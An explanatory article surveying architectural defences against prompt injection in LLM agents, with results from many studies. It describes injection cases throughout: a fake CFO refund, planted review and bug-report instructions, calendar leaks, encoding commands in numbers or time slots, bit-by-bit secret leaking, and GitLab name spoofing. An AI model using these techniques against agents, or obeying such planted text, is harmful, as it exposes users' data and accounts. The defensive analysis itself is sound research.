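*Prompts Don't Protect* (Uppala, 2026) compared giving a model a written list of permitted tools with hiding the forbidden ones, so the restriction applied to whole tools rather than a single argument. Three models each faced 200 tasks that tempted them to use a tool outside their role. In one task, somebody claiming to be the chief financial officer told an analytics agent to refund $5,000. When the models could see all the tools and had the written list, Llama 3.1 8B chose a forbidden tool in 4.0% of tasks, Claude Haiku 4.5 in 11.5% and Qwen 2.5 7B in 37.0%. When a program hid the forbidden tools, none of the models chose one. The test probably exaggerates how often the written list fails, because the models had to call a tool and could not refuse.

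Uppala also gave the models 140 legitimate requests, this time letting them decide whether to call a tool. Hiding the forbidden tools instead of using the written list raised Llama's success rate from 77.9% to 82.1% but lowered Qwen's from 60.7% to 48.6%. Haiku's was about 19% with either method. Hiding tools protected every model equally, but its effect on usefulness varied by model.

### When a manager really wants a comparison

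The plausible request in the hotel experiment was ordinary, and the login covered both hotels. A manager who really wanted the comparison would have got it from the first tool but not from the second. The server's refusals therefore measure lost utility as well as protection. Baig and colleagues did not measure how often managers need such comparisons, so the size of the loss is unknown.

Managers with a legitimate reason to compare hotels need another way to do it. If they mostly want totals, a developer could add a tool called `compare_hotels` that takes no arguments and returns the revenue and occupancy of every hotel on the login. An injected instruction could still make the agent call this tool, but the tool would return a few totals instead of thousands of guests' bookings. For anything more detailed, the manager could choose the hotels in an ordinary menu before the session starts,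 and the identity provider would issue a token for those hotels only.

The researchers propose a more convenient design for tools that have to work on one hotel at a time. The agent first calls a tool that lists the hotels on the login, then picks one, and the server checks the choice. But this lets the agent choose the hotel again, so whoever steers the agent can once more reach every hotel on the login, as in the formula.

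The production system has the same limit. Its token lists all the user's hotels, and the researchers acknowledge that they aimed only to keep every read within that list. An agent working for the area manager can still read 10,000 reservations. The redesign makes it much harder for a forgotten filter or a forged identity to give the agent access to other companies' hotels, but it does not confine the agent to the hotel the manager has in mind. In the experiment, the tool without an identifier kept the agent to the intended hotel because each session's scope contained a single hotel. A developer who wants that protection has to issue equally narrow tokens.

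Sharma and colleagues argue that this gap is built into OAuth, the standard most websites use to let a program act for a user. OAuth can permit a program to make transfers, but it can't limit the program to transferring exactly $100 to Bob. In their system, PAuth, each server receives the user's written task and works out which calls the task implies, including the arguments. The server allows those calls and asks the user about any others. In tests, PAuth accepted all 100 legitimate tasks and blocked all 634 adversarial calls.

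With a system like this, asking for a comparison of two hotels would itself authorize the agent to read both, and a guest's note could not authorize it to read a third. But PAuth relies on a language model to translate the task into the expected calls, and it assumes that the task is unambiguous. A request like "Compare us with our other hotels" might be too ambiguous.

### Keeping the filter fast

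A login that covers several hotels also makes the database's work harder. To find one hotel's reservations, a database uses an index, a sorted list that leads straight to the right rows. For a set of hotels, a developer might write the filter like this, where `@hotels` is the list from the token:

```sql
SELECT * FROM reservations
WHERE JSON_CONTAINS(@hotels, CAST(hotel_id AS JSON))
```

This returns the right rows, but slowly. Because `hotel_id` is inside a function, the database cannot jump to the right part of the index and has to go through all of it. The researchers' rewrite turns the list into a small temporary table and joins it to the reservations:

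```sql
SELECT reservations.* FROM reservations
JOIN JSON_TABLE(@hotels, '$[*]'
     COLUMNS (id INT PATH '$')) AS allowed
  ON reservations.hotel_id = allowed.id
```

The database can now look up each permitted hotel in the index. With three hotels, the median time on the largest indexed table fell from 5.8 seconds to 0.1 seconds, a 57-fold difference. The rewrite helps only if the table has an index on the hotel column, and about a fifth of the tables the researchers checked lacked one.

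The production server's module instead writes the permitted hotels directly into each query. A query for three hotels took about 0.45 seconds, mostly because the database lacked a suitable index for skipping deleted records. Ten hotels took about 1.1 seconds, and 15 took 10 seconds, when the database switched to a less suitable index. The stronger version, with the filter in the database, took 1.5 seconds for 20 hotels. Baig and colleagues expect the mechanisms to apply to other systems, but not the exact figures, which come from a single database under live traffic.

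The filter can add much less delay where each user belongs to only one group. In *Securing the Agent*, Arceo and Narsing (2026) tested a document search for three departments in which the server took the user's department from a token. The protection added about 19 milliseconds to a search, while the model took several seconds to answer. None of 90 injection attempts retrieved another department's documents. Without the filter, 62% to 80% of them did, but this was a weaker baseline than the hotel study's, where even the first tool had a correct check.

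Their filter could also make the search less useful, because some search engines rank everyone's documents first and remove the forbidden ones afterwards. If other departments' documents fill the top places, the user may get nothing. In a test of this method, the share of relevant passages returned in the top five fell from 100% in a collection of 100 passages to 0.2% in one of 50,000. Arceo and Narsing recommend search engines that apply the filter during the search, which avoids the problem.

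## Passing only numbers and fixed choices between models

The redesigned hotel server limited what an agent could request, but the agent still read the guests' notes, any of which could contain an injected instruction. Another approach keeps untrusted text away from the model that calls the tools. That model must then act on text it cannot read, so its usefulness depends on how much information about the text it is allowed to receive.

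### An agent that never sees its results

The strictest design gives the agent no feedback from its actions. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) calls this the action-selector pattern. The model reads the user's request and picks one or more calls from a fixed list. Ordinary software makes the calls and never passes the results back to the model. A customer service chatbot of this kind might fetch a link to the customer's last order, or direct the customer to the settings for a password or payment card. An action can also be a template, such as a stored SQL query with placeholders for the model to fill in.

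An instruction hidden in an order record cannot influence this agent, because the agent never reads the record. Hostile text in the user's own message still reaches the model, but it can only make the model pick a different action from the list. However, no step can depend on the outcome of an earlier one. For example, the chatbot cannot check whether an order has shipped and cancel it if it has not, unless a developer has written a single tool that does both.

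### Handling text only by name

The programmer Simon Willison proposed a more flexible design, the Dual LLM pattern, in 2023. A privileged model plans the work and calls the tools but sees no untrusted text. A quarantined model reads the untrusted text but has no tools. Between them sits an orchestrator, an ordinary program that stores the quarantined model's answers in sealed variables, which the privileged model can refer to by name but cannot open. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give the example of an agent that has to find an email address in a document and write to it:

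1. The privileged model asks the quarantined model to find the address.
2. The quarantined model reads the document and answers. The orchestrator stores the answer as `$VAR`.
3. The privileged model calls `send_email` with `$VAR` as the recipient.
4. The orchestrator replaces `$VAR` with the address and sends the email.

The same method works for longer texts. In an example from *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025), the planning model sends an isolated model the name of a variable that holds some unread emails, with an instruction to summarize them. The planning model can then send the summary to someone without seeing either the summary or the emails.

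Text in the document cannot add a tool call or replace one tool with another, because the model that chooses the calls never reads it. But the text can still affect the variable's value. If an injection causes the quarantined model to return the attacker's address, the orchestrator will send the email there.

The privileged model also cannot make decisions that depend on the text. It can forward a sealed bug report but cannot fix the bug. *Twin Agent* (Hu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026) tested this on real bugs from open-source projects. With GPT-5.2, an unprotected agent fixed 61.2% of them. A privileged model given no information from the report fixed none.

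Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe an agent that collects the month's invoices and emails them to the accounts department. A separate quarantined model reads each file and answers only whether it is an invoice. A malicious file can cause the model to answer yes wrongly, so that the agent includes the file in the email, but the file's author could have achieved that by writing an invoice.

### Four permitted types

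*Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues, 2026) turned this idea into a general method. The quarantined model may return whole numbers, decimals, yes-or-no values and choices from a list that the developer has checked. It may combine several of these in one message, called a handoff, and it may fill sealed variables. It may not return free-form text to the privileged model. Most model providers can force an answer to fit such a schema. The privileged model can send any information to the quarantined model, because the quarantined model has no tools to misuse.

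The researchers built three agents, each in an ordinary version and a protected one.

| Agent | Model | Test cases | Utility, ordinary | Utility, protected | Attack success, ordinary | Attack success, protected |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Shopping | GPT-4o | 500 | 21.8% | 22.4% | 31.7% | 0% |
| Calendar | GPT-4o | 100 | 90.0% | 91.0% | 63.0% | 0% |
| Bug fixing | GPT-5.2 | 180 | 68.3% | 45.0% | 98.9% | 0% |

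In WebShop, a test environment with about 1.2 million products, the shopping agent had to find and buy one that matched a user's wishes. It succeeded if it got the full score in at least three of five attempts. WebShop has no product reviews, so the researchers generated some with GPT-4o. To attack the agent, they added text to one of the right product's reviews, calling the product a banned substance and telling the agent to leave the page. In the protected version, the quarantined model scored each review from 0 to 10 on how strongly it supported the product and on how relevant it was. The privileged model saw the number of reviews and the median of each score.

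The protection did not reduce the shopping agent's performance, but this test could hardly have shown a loss, because WebShop scores a purchase by whether it fits the requested features and price, and the reviews were added later. The protection also covers only the reviews, so the privileged model still reads the rest of the product page, where a dishonest seller could place an injection.

The calendar agent arranged meetings by email, and a malicious correspondent asked it for the user's whole calendar. The quarantined model reduced the emails to a list of suggested times, each chosen from a fixed set of one-hour slots. The privileged model compared these with the calendar and either booked a meeting or proposed other times, which a separate model turned into an email. Fixed choices suit this task because the agent needs to know little beyond a time slot. The ordinary agent leaked private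 event descriptions in 63 of the 100 conversations, and the protected agent leaked them in none.

However, the protected agent also used a sealed variable to copy a free-form description of the meeting from the emails into the calendar. The privileged model can read the calendar, so an instruction in the description could reach it the next time the user arranges a meeting. The experiment did not test for this, because it counted only leaks within a single conversation. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes the same delay with an invoice that an agent stores on Monday and pays on Tuesday. Its system keeps stored text sealed in later tasks too, and shows the planning model only a description of what each item is.

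### Why the coding agent lost a third of its fixes

Jacob and colleagues ran the bug-fixing agent on SWE-bench Lite, a set of real problems from GitHub with tests that check each repair. The attacker added a sentence to the bug report asking the agent to create an unrelated file called `pipipi.py`. The ordinary agent created the file in 178 of 180 cases. The request was harmless, and GPT-5.2 might follow an openly destructive one less often.

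In the protected version, the quarantined model read the report, explored the code and returned a handoff. The handoff contained one of 52 categories of bug, one of three estimates of the size of the repair, and a list of code regions. Each region had a file number, a first and last line, and one of eight roles, such as "region suspected to contain the bug".

The researchers added another stage to make up for the missing text. A planning model that had never seen the report read the handoff and the code, and wrote three possible repair plans in ordinary English. A quarantined judge, which had seen the report, compared the plans and returned only the number of the best one. The privileged model then received that plan along with the handoff. Free text was safe in the plans because the planning model had not received any untrusted text.

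Even so, the number of bugs the agent fixed fell from 123 to 81. Jacob and colleagues attribute this to the role of ordinary language in bug reports. Suppose someone reports that a program shows dates before 1970 one day early. The handoff can indicate that lines 40 to 58 of a certain file contain a calculation error. But it cannot include an example of the wrong output or a description of the correct output, so the privileged model has to work out the error from the code alone. The judge can help only if one of the three plans is right.

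The schema was also hard to design. The researchers settled on it only after considerable testing on a separate set of tasks, and they leave automating this work to future research. They expect stronger models to reduce the loss, which is plausible for bugs that a careful reader can find in the code. It is less plausible where the code is consistent and only the report shows that users wanted something else.

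### Getting the lost detail back with short hints

Hu and colleagues, who include several of the same researchers, recovered the loss by lifting the ban on free text. In Twin Agent, one model reads the bug report and can send a hint of up to 100 characters at each step. The other model edits the code and runs commands, but never sees the report. The first model sees everything the second has done, so a hint needs to contain only what the second model still lacks for its next step.

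This agent fixed 62.5% of 232 bugs, compared with 61.2% for the unprotected agent. The success rate of simple attacks fell from 97.0% to zero. Each task cost about twice as much. On AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants injections in simulated office, chat, travel and banking tasks, the researchers allowed 200 characters. Overall utility stayed about the same, at 62.9% against 61.9%, but in the chat tasks it fell from 90.5% to 66.7%.

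Twin Agent's security relies on the observation that strong models are hard to hijack with a short text. A second model also screens each hint for injections, and the model that edits the code has a written reminder to treat hints as background information. To try to defeat these protections, the researchers used a language model to refine hostile hints over 100 rounds, then planted the hints in bug reports with an instruction to copy them word for word.

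In a separate test, the model that read the reports forwarded the hostile hints every time. In the full test, hostile hints got past the screening at least once in 57 of 232 tasks, and the agent carried out the attack in 11 tasks (4.7%). When the researchers ran those 11 tasks five more times each, the attack failed in all 55 runs. The attacks' success therefore seems to depend partly on chance, so an attacker who can file many reports might still succeed.

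In the hotel experiment's terms, Twin Agent replaces structural assurance with behavioral assurance. A developer might reasonably accept this if a person reviews the agent's patches before anyone uses them, but not if the agent can publish its own code.

### How much a typed value can carry

Jacob and colleagues argue that a whole number cannot contain an instruction, because an instruction needs some free-form text. Taken literally, this is wrong, since computers store all text as numbers. The letters "r" and "m" have the codes 114 and 109, so `rm`, the shell's command for deleting files, can be written as

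114 × 256 + 109 = 29,293.

The 16 characters of "delete all tests" become a 39-digit number in the same way. A whole number with no upper limit can hold a text of any length, and so can a decimal with unlimited digits.

A choice among *k* options carries at most log<sub>2</sub>(*k*) bits, and a list of *n* such choices carries at most *n* × log<sub>2</sub>(*k*) bits. Each character in a text of lowercase letters and spaces is one of 27 symbols, so it carries at most log<sub>2</sub>(27), or about 4.75, bits. The table gives the capacity of the handoffs above, assuming a calendar with nine slots a day for seven days and a project with 4,000 files of 1,000 lines each.

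| Value | Possibilities | Bits | Characters of text |
|---|---|---|---|
| Yes or no | 2 | 1 | 0 |
| The best of three plans | 3 | 1.6 | 0 |
| One time slot | 63 | 6.0 | 1 |
| Two review scores from 0 to 10 | 121 | 6.9 | 1 |
| One code region | about 16 billion | 33.9 | 7 |
| A 64-bit whole number | 2<sup>64</sup> | 64 | 13 |
| Bug category, repair size and ten code regions | about 10<sup>104</sup> | 346 | 72 |

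Lists need a maximum length, just as numbers need a range. There are more time slots than letters, so an attacker could let Sunday at 8:00 stand for "a", Sunday at 9:00 for "b", and so on. A list of 16 slots could then spell "delete all tests". Jacob and colleagues therefore recommend a small upper limit on list length, but they give no figure, and they let the quarantined model choose the length in both the calendar agent and the bug-fixing agent. If the calendar agent accepted at most three different slots, sorted by time, only 41,728 lists would be possible. Each list could then carry at most 15.3 bits, enough for three letters, and the agent could still negotiate a meeting.

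A value that can encode an instruction is dangerous only if something decodes it. A model that receives a 39-digit line number has no obvious reason to turn it into letters. Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, states the condition exactly. Let σ(*v*) be what remains of an untrusted text *v* after cleaning, and let *parse* give the instruction that a model reads in a text, or ⊥ if it reads none. The cleaning works if

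*parse*(σ(*v*)) = ⊥ for every *v*.

The condition depends on the model as well as the cleaning, because no schema could satisfy it if the model read every value as an instruction. With a narrow range, a developer could test the condition directly by giving the model all 121 pairs of review scores. But 10<sup>104</sup> possible handoffs are too many to test, so the developer has to rely on the model not to find hidden messages in line numbers.

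How easily an attacker can exploit a message depends on how the receiving model decodes it, as well as on how many bits it carries. A Twin Agent hint of 100 lowercase letters and spaces carries about 475 bits, roughly as much as 14 code regions passed in handoffs. But the hint is in English, which every language model already understands, so an attacker would presumably find it much easier to exploit than the code regions.

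An attacker can sometimes get around the capacity limit by using a value as a pointer. A code region directs the privileged model to specific lines of a file, and the model will probably read them. If the attacker has already added a page of instructions to the project's documentation, the 34 bits of one region are enough to point the privileged model to the whole page. Jacob and colleagues rule out this attack by assuming that the project's own files contain no malicious instructions.

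Lists of fixed choices can have a similar weakness if the developer doesn't write them. In the bug-fixing agent, a program replaces each file number with the file's path before the privileged model sees it, so whoever named the file wrote some of the text the model reads. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues count file names among the things an attacker may control.

### False answers of the right type

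A typed value can be false even if it contains no instruction. Jacob and colleagues acknowledge that an attacker could persuade the quarantined model to return misleading information, but they treat this as a different problem from prompt injection and did not measure it. Their attack success rates of zero therefore mean only that agents did not follow the planted instructions. Attackers may still be able to influence the results.

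An attacker might send the bug-fixing agent a false report that a working login check is faulty. The handoff would then label the check "incorrect conditional logic", and the privileged model might try to fix it. The attacker cannot dictate the new code, but any change to a correct login check is a risk. The experiment would have counted this as a successful defense because it only checked whether the patch contained the extra file.

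Combining several independent answers can limit the damage. Suppose five reviews give a product support scores of 7, 8, 8, 9 and 9. If an attacker controls one of the reviews that scored 9 and changes its score to 0, the average falls from 8.2 to 6.4, but the median stays at 8. An attacker needs to write most of the reviews to control the median. The privileged model should also check answers itself when it can. In Twin Agent, the model that edited the code usually compared hints with the code and found the real bug, even when the hints were hostile.

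Some answers cannot be checked this way. An account number is a whole number, and the attacker's is as valid as anyone else's. Girrens and Wang point out that an invoice with the wrong account number can divert a payment even if the agent carries out exactly the steps the user intended. Their system can refuse to pass data from outside sources to sensitive tools. This reduced the attack success rate on AgentDojo to zero, but utility fell from 53.0% to 29.0%, because many legitimate tasks, such as paying bills, need such data.

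One alternative is to accept important values only from the user. *CapLite* (2026) describes a system in which, for any action that changes something, every recipient, account and amount must exactly match a value in the user's request. Injected text can still change dates, the wording of messages, what the agent reads, and its final answer to the user. An injection can also cause harm through an approved account. *Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (2026) examines a banking agent that reads a bill containing an injected request for an extra payment. A defense that blocks every injected payment to an account outside an approved list does not stop an injection from making the agent pay a listed company twice.

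### Leaking a secret through a choice

A false answer can also reveal private data. Dongol analyzed this in Isabelle/HOL, a program that checks every step of a mathematical proof. The analysis compares an agent with a reference agent that follows the same plan under the same restrictions, but whose model never obeys untrusted text. An agent leaks if it visibly behaves differently in two cases where the attacker sends the same material and only the user's private data differs. It still counts as secure if the attacker could also have told the two cases apart with the reference agent, perhaps by sending a different email. This definition allows disclosures that are part of the task, such as telling someone who requests a meeting when the user is free.

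In the Dual LLM pattern, the plan is fixed before the agent reads any untrusted text, and the quarantined model only answers questions. An injection therefore can't add a tool call and can only make an answer wrong. Dongol assumes the worst case, in which the attacker can make the answer depend in any way on what the question contains.

In the first example, the agent reads the user's private notes and an email from the attacker, asks the quarantined model to write a reply based on both, and sends it. Normally the reply would depend only on the email, but an injection can make the quarantined model copy the notes into the reply. The plan still runs exactly as written, and the notes reach the attacker.

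A second version labels data as private or public. Anything the quarantined model computes from private data is also labeled private, and a program refuses to send private data to the attacker. Dongol proved that this version is secure whatever the quarantined model does, provided the attacker cannot see the refused messages. But the agent cannot do its job, because the program also refuses to send the honest reply, which the quarantined model wrote with access to the private notes.

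The third version sends no text from the quarantined model. The plan has that model answer a question, then sends the attacker 1 or 0 depending on the answer. The labels allow this because both numbers are public constants from the plan. But an injection can make the answer depend on the private notes, and the attacker then learns something about the notes from which number arrives. Dongol proved that this agent leaks.

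A narrow type limits how fast an agent leaks information, but not how much it leaks over many messages. If the notes contain a four-digit code and the agent answers every email with one bit, an attacker can ask each time whether the code is in the upper half of the remaining possibilities. Since log<sub>2</sub>(10,000) is about 13.3, 14 emails are enough to find the code.

Labels that also follow the plan's decisions could block this leak. CaMeL, a system built on the Dual LLM pattern, has a strict mode designed to do so, but Dongol did not analyze that mode. Developers can also avoid the leak by asking a question that the quarantined model can answer from the email alone. If the model never receives the notes, its answer cannot reveal them. In Jacob and colleagues' calendar agent, the quarantined model likewise receives the emails, and only the privileged model receives the calendar. The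 correspondent can still learn something about the user's free hours from the times the agent proposes, and could learn more by repeatedly turning them down. The experiment did not count this as a leak because it checked only for text from the event descriptions.

Dongol's proofs apply only to agents with a fixed plan, and they cover leaks but not harmful actions that reveal nothing. Jacob and colleagues' privileged models choose their next step after each handoff, so the proofs do not cover them directly. The same kind of leak can still occur whenever a quarantined model sees both a secret and an attacker's text, and the attacker can observe what the privileged model does with the quarantined model's answer.

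## Web agents that see masked pages or call typed website operations

In the previous cases, untrusted text reached the agent through a few known channels, such as emails or bug reports. An agent that browses the web for its user encounters it on almost every page.

The usual browsing tools also make it hard to limit what an agent can do. A click takes a very narrow argument, just a screen position or the identifier of a page element. But Piet, Chow and colleagues (2026) point out in *Position* that clicking the same place can open a product, submit a purchase or delete an item, depending on the page. A developer also can't list the safe clicks in advance, because many buttons appear only after the agent has clicked on something else.

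A product page may combine the shop's own buttons with a seller's description, customers' reviews and advertisements. Parker (2025), in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, names user reviews and embedded third-party content among the places where an injection can appear. Most web agents read the page, choose an action and then read the resulting page. The model's input therefore includes strangers' text whenever it makes a decision, often while it is logged in as the user. It can't just skip that text, because the user may have asked for a summary of the reviews.

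### Placeholders in place of strangers' text

One solution lets the agent click on a page's elements but hides untrusted text from it. Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues (2026) describe this approach in *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees*. A browser stores each page as a tree of labeled elements, and reviews and comments usually have their own labels, so a program can find them without interpreting what they say. The program replaces each one with a placeholder such as `id: merchant-name:3`. The agent still sees the layout, the site's own text and the kind of content behind each placeholder, and it can click on a masked link without seeing the link's text.

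When the agent needs information from a masked element, it puts a question to a quarantined model. A question about a review might look like this:

```json
{
  "target": { "qllm_id": "shop:reviews:0" },
  "query": "How many stars does this customer give?",
  "return_type": "int",
  "return_constraints": { "min": 1, "max": 5 }
}
```

The answer must be a yes-or-no value, a whole number, a decimal, a date or a choice from a list. The agent has to state a minimum and a maximum for numbers, and list at most ten options for choices. It can ask about each element at most five times per task, which makes it hard to spell out hidden text letter by letter.

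In Jacob and colleagues' design, developers had to decide in advance what the quarantined model could report. Here the agent writes its questions as it works, so it can handle tasks no developer foresaw. It sets the range of permitted answers before the quarantined model reads the text, so an attacker doesn't influence that range.

Some tasks need a free-form answer. If the agent declares a task unsolvable, it can ask the quarantined model for one. The user sees the question, the hidden content and the proposed answer, and can approve, edit or reject the answer. The protection then depends on the user noticing an injection.

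It also depends on correct labels. Nikolić and colleagues assume that the site's owner is honest and marks the parts that other people wrote. They labeled GitLab, Booking.com and Reddit by hand, which took 15 to 30 rules per site. For sites that provide no labels, they tested whether Claude Sonnet 4.5 could write the rules, after removing all the text from the pages so that an injection could not influence the labeling. An attacker needs only one unmasked element, and the model missed about one in ten kinds of untrusted element on GitLab and one in fifteen on Booking.com, but none on Reddit.

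### What masking cost

Nikolić and colleagues built ten websites, including a bank, a forum and a job board, and wrote ten tasks for each. Half of the tasks, such as sorting products by name, needed only trusted content. The rest needed masked content, including one in which the agent had to count the steps in an article about chemical spills.

Claude Sonnet 4.5, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GPT-5.4 completed about as many tasks with masking as without it. Masking raised the median cost per task by a factor of 1.05 to 1.84, depending on the model and the type of task. About 15% of tasks became cheaper. The researchers attribute this to less cluttered pages, where agents were more likely to use a site's filter than to scroll through a long list.

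The same people designed these sites, the tasks and the defense, so the test on GitLab, a widely used service for storing code and discussing changes to it, is more informative. The researchers ran the real software and took 41 task templates from WebArena, a benchmark of everyday tasks on self-hosted websites. The masked agents solved most of them but declared four unsolvable, all of which needed free-form text. Three required details such as the names or email addresses of a project's top contributors, and one required changing a title in a file. Once the agents could request text with the user's approval, they did as well as agents without masking. The test does not show how carefully real users would read such requests.

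The researchers measured security with WASP, a benchmark that plants injections in GitLab. Its original attacks no longer worked on recent models, so they wrote stronger ones. The agent had to read an issue to decide which of two comments to post, and the issue contained an instruction to do something else first, such as delete the project. A second model rewrote failed attacks for up to five rounds. Attacks on Claude Sonnet 4 succeeded 17% of the time with no defense, 8% with a written warning and 0% with masking. With masking, the agent also completed every legitimate task. When the researchers left the issue's description unmasked, as if someone had mislabeled it, the success rate of attacks rose to about 6%.

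### A false answer that picks the wrong project

Masking stops strangers from giving the agent instructions, but they can still give it wrong information. Nikolić and colleagues asked Claude Sonnet 4.6 to play an attacker who could make the quarantined model return any answer of the permitted type, to see what this attacker could achieve on GitLab. Most of the attacks only wasted the agent's time, for example by falsely reporting that an action had failed, but two could do real damage.

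In one of these, the user asks the agent to invite Marko to a project called `dotfiles`. The project names are masked, so the agent asks the quarantined model about each one in turn, "Is this project name dotfiles?", and acts on the first yes. If the list includes an attacker's project whose name tricks the model into answering yes, the agent invites Marko to that project. In the other, the user wants to add `stefan01` to a project. The attacker registers a name such as `stefan_i_am_the_right_person`, which appears in the same search, and the agent may add the attacker instead.

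Both attacks require the attacker to anticipate the user's task and to influence a model using only a name. The researchers suggest asking about all the candidates and treating two positive answers as a sign of tampering. For exact names, a simpler remedy is to compare the strings with an ordinary program, which does this reliably and won't report a match between different strings, however they are worded.

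### Writing the program before reading anything

A program can do much more of an agent's work than compare names. CaMeL, which Google DeepMind introduced in 2025, has a privileged model turn the user's request into a complete program before any tool runs. An interpreter then executes the program and keeps the tools' results in variables. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, welcomed it after two and a half years of what Willison considered alarmingly little progress. For the task with Marko, such a program could look like this:

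```python
for project in list_my_projects():
    if project.name == "dotfiles":
        invite(project.id, user="marko", role="guest")
```

This design still allows composition. The output of `list_my_projects` becomes part of the input of `invite`, and a longer program could combine dozens of tools with loops and conditions. An interpreter also runs text written by a model, which was the danger sign in the earlier cases. But the model writes the program after seeing only the user's request and the tool descriptions. As in the Dual LLM pattern, text that arrives later can change a value or determine which existing branch runs, but it can't add a tool call to the program.

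CaMeL's planner therefore has to write the code for handling a tool's result before anyone has seen that result, whereas an ordinary agent can look at the result and work out its structure. CaMeL agents did reasonably well on two benchmarks only after *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) added a description of the return value to every tool. The paper describes this as a modest, one-time job.

*SecureClaw* (2026) reports that CaMeL stopped all 629 attacks on AgentDojo but completed only 29 of 97 legitimate tasks (29.9%). SecureClaw, a competing system, completed 59. SecureClaw's developers ran the comparison and had to adapt CaMeL's code for it, so CaMeL's completion rate may understate its performance.

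Planning without seeing the screen is even harder when the agent acts by clicking. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) applies the approach to agents that operate a computer through its screen. The plans averaged 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about five and four on AgentDojo, because they had to cover many screens the planner could not see. Piet and colleagues add that a model still has to find each button on the live screen. A misleading image can make it choose the wrong spot, and the preplanned click then has an effect that was not part of the plan.

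### Named operations for a whole website

Piet and colleagues, at UC Berkeley, conclude that web agents should have typed operations such as "search the catalog" or "post a comment", whose effects are known before the agent starts. A general-purpose `click` operation wouldn't meet this requirement. Operations can also do too much. A `checkout` operation, for instance, must let the program choose the shipping and payment methods instead of setting them silently.

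Several of the same researchers then built Baya, an agent based on this principle (Chow, Zhu and colleagues, 2026, *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm*). Baya works with a typed interface that developers prepare for each website. For example, an operation called `search_products` takes a search text and returns a list of products, each with a name, price, rating and a few other fields. Its description also specifies what must be true before the call, whether the call changes anything on the site, and which errors it can produce.

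If a website has its own programming interface, the operation uses it. Otherwise, a script operates the site through a browser, clicking the buttons its developer chose.

Baya handles a request in four steps:

1. A coding agent receives the request and a catalog of operations. It has no access to the website or the rest of the internet. GitLab alone has 1,028 operations, so the agent searches the catalog and opens only the descriptions it needs.
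2. The agent writes a Python program and tests it with made-up responses. The program may do ordinary calculations and call the listed operations, but it may not run other code or contact other addresses.
3. A separate process runs the program on the live website with the user's login.
4. If the program fails, the coding agent receives an error message and can revise the program, up to three times.

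In the last step, an error message carries information from the live site back to the model that writes the code. The message may name a missing field, but it must not repeat anything from a review, a username or other text that a stranger could have written. Chow and colleagues rely on the interface's developers to ensure this. Their security claim doesn't cover an operation that breaks the rule, for example by quoting a product's name in an error.

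Programs can call a quarantined model to judge text that fixed rules can't. For example, searching reviews for the word "small" isn't enough to find customers who thought a pair of headphones had small ear cups. In the tests, only 11 of 627 programs called a model while they ran, so no model read anything from the website in the other 616.

### More completed tasks and a longer wait

Chow and colleagues tested Baya on 581 tasks from WebArena Verified, an audited version of WebArena. The tasks covered GitLab, an online shop, the shop's administration pages, and a forum running the Postmill software. The researchers compared Baya with two step-by-step agents, one with both a browser and the operations in Baya's catalog, and one with only a browser. Utility is averaged across Claude Sonnet 4.6, Gemini 3.5 Flash and GPT-5.6 Luna.

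| Agent | Utility | Attacks that influenced the agent | Time per task | Model cost per task |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Baya | 77.8% | 0% | 327 seconds | $0.70 |
| Step by step, with catalog and browser | 66.7% | 16.2% | 87 seconds | $0.34 |
| Step by step, with browser only | 55.1% | 25.5% | 60 seconds | $0.16 |

The attack figures come from WASP, with DeepSeek-V4-Flash in place of GPT-5.6 Luna. Chow and colleagues call them attack success rates, but the rates count every attempt that influenced what the agent did along the way. Attackers reached their final goal in only one of the 12 combinations of step-by-step agent, model and website, and in only 5.6% of attempts there. The catalog alone gave no reliable protection. With Gemini 3.5 Flash on the forum, the agent that had the catalog followed injections in 52.8% of attempts, compared with 27.8% for the agent without it.

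Part of Baya's advantage in utility seems to come from writing and testing the whole program before running it. One task asked for a customer's completed orders and total spending over four months. The step-by-step agent filtered the orders by status and date but not by customer, so it reported someone else's figures. Baya's program filtered by all three, and its tests checked the query.

But buttons are sometimes the better interface. To repeat an old order, a browser agent can open the order history and click "Reorder". Through the shop's programming interface, an agent has to look up the customer, find the order, create a cart, add the item, enter the shipping and billing details, and submit the new order. With GPT-5.6 Luna, the step-by-step agent with the catalog did better than Baya on both the shop and its administration pages.

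Much of Baya's overall lead also comes from the forum, where it beat both other agents by at least 39.6 percentage points with every model. Without the forum, its lead over the agent with the catalog shrinks from 11 points to about 4. With the forum still excluded, the two are practically level with Gemini 3.5 Flash, and the step-by-step agent is about six points ahead with GPT-5.6 Luna. It is safer to conclude that fixing the program in advance need not reduce utility than that it generally raises utility.

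An earlier version of Baya wrote its plans in a fixed format with a few operations for filtering, repeating and branching, instead of in Python. With Claude Sonnet 4.6, its average utility across the four sites was 66.9%, compared with 82.4% for the Python version. Since the attacker can't influence the program in either version, the more restricted format made the agent considerably less useful while adding little protection against injections. However, it was much faster, at 82 seconds per task.

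### Masking and Baya on GitLab

The two systems have been run on the same test only on GitLab, because masking needs labels for each site and the published code includes suitable ones only for GitLab. With Claude Sonnet 4.6 as the main model, Baya completed 143 of 154 tasks (92.9%) and the masked agent completed 116 (75.3%). Neither followed any of the 48 injections, and both completed all the accompanying legitimate tasks. The masked agent averaged 469 seconds and $4.01 per task, both well above Baya's averages.

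The way each system handles free-form text probably explains some of the gap. When a user asks for the email address of a project's top contributor, the masked agent can't read the address without the user's approval. Baya's program can count the commits, fetch the address and print it, because it passes the address along as a value that no planning model has to process, much like the sealed variables in the Dual LLM pattern.

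Baya's developers ran this comparison on one website with one main model. The masked agent did better than the ordinary browser agent, which completed 64.9% of the GitLab tasks, but the masked agent could take up to 120 steps per task, compared with 30 for the ordinary agent.

### Building an interface for every site

Masking a site takes a few dozen rules, but Baya needs a description of everything an agent might have to do there. Chow and colleagues built Baya's interfaces by hand. They went through each site's API and documentation, corrected the descriptions and filled in what was missing.

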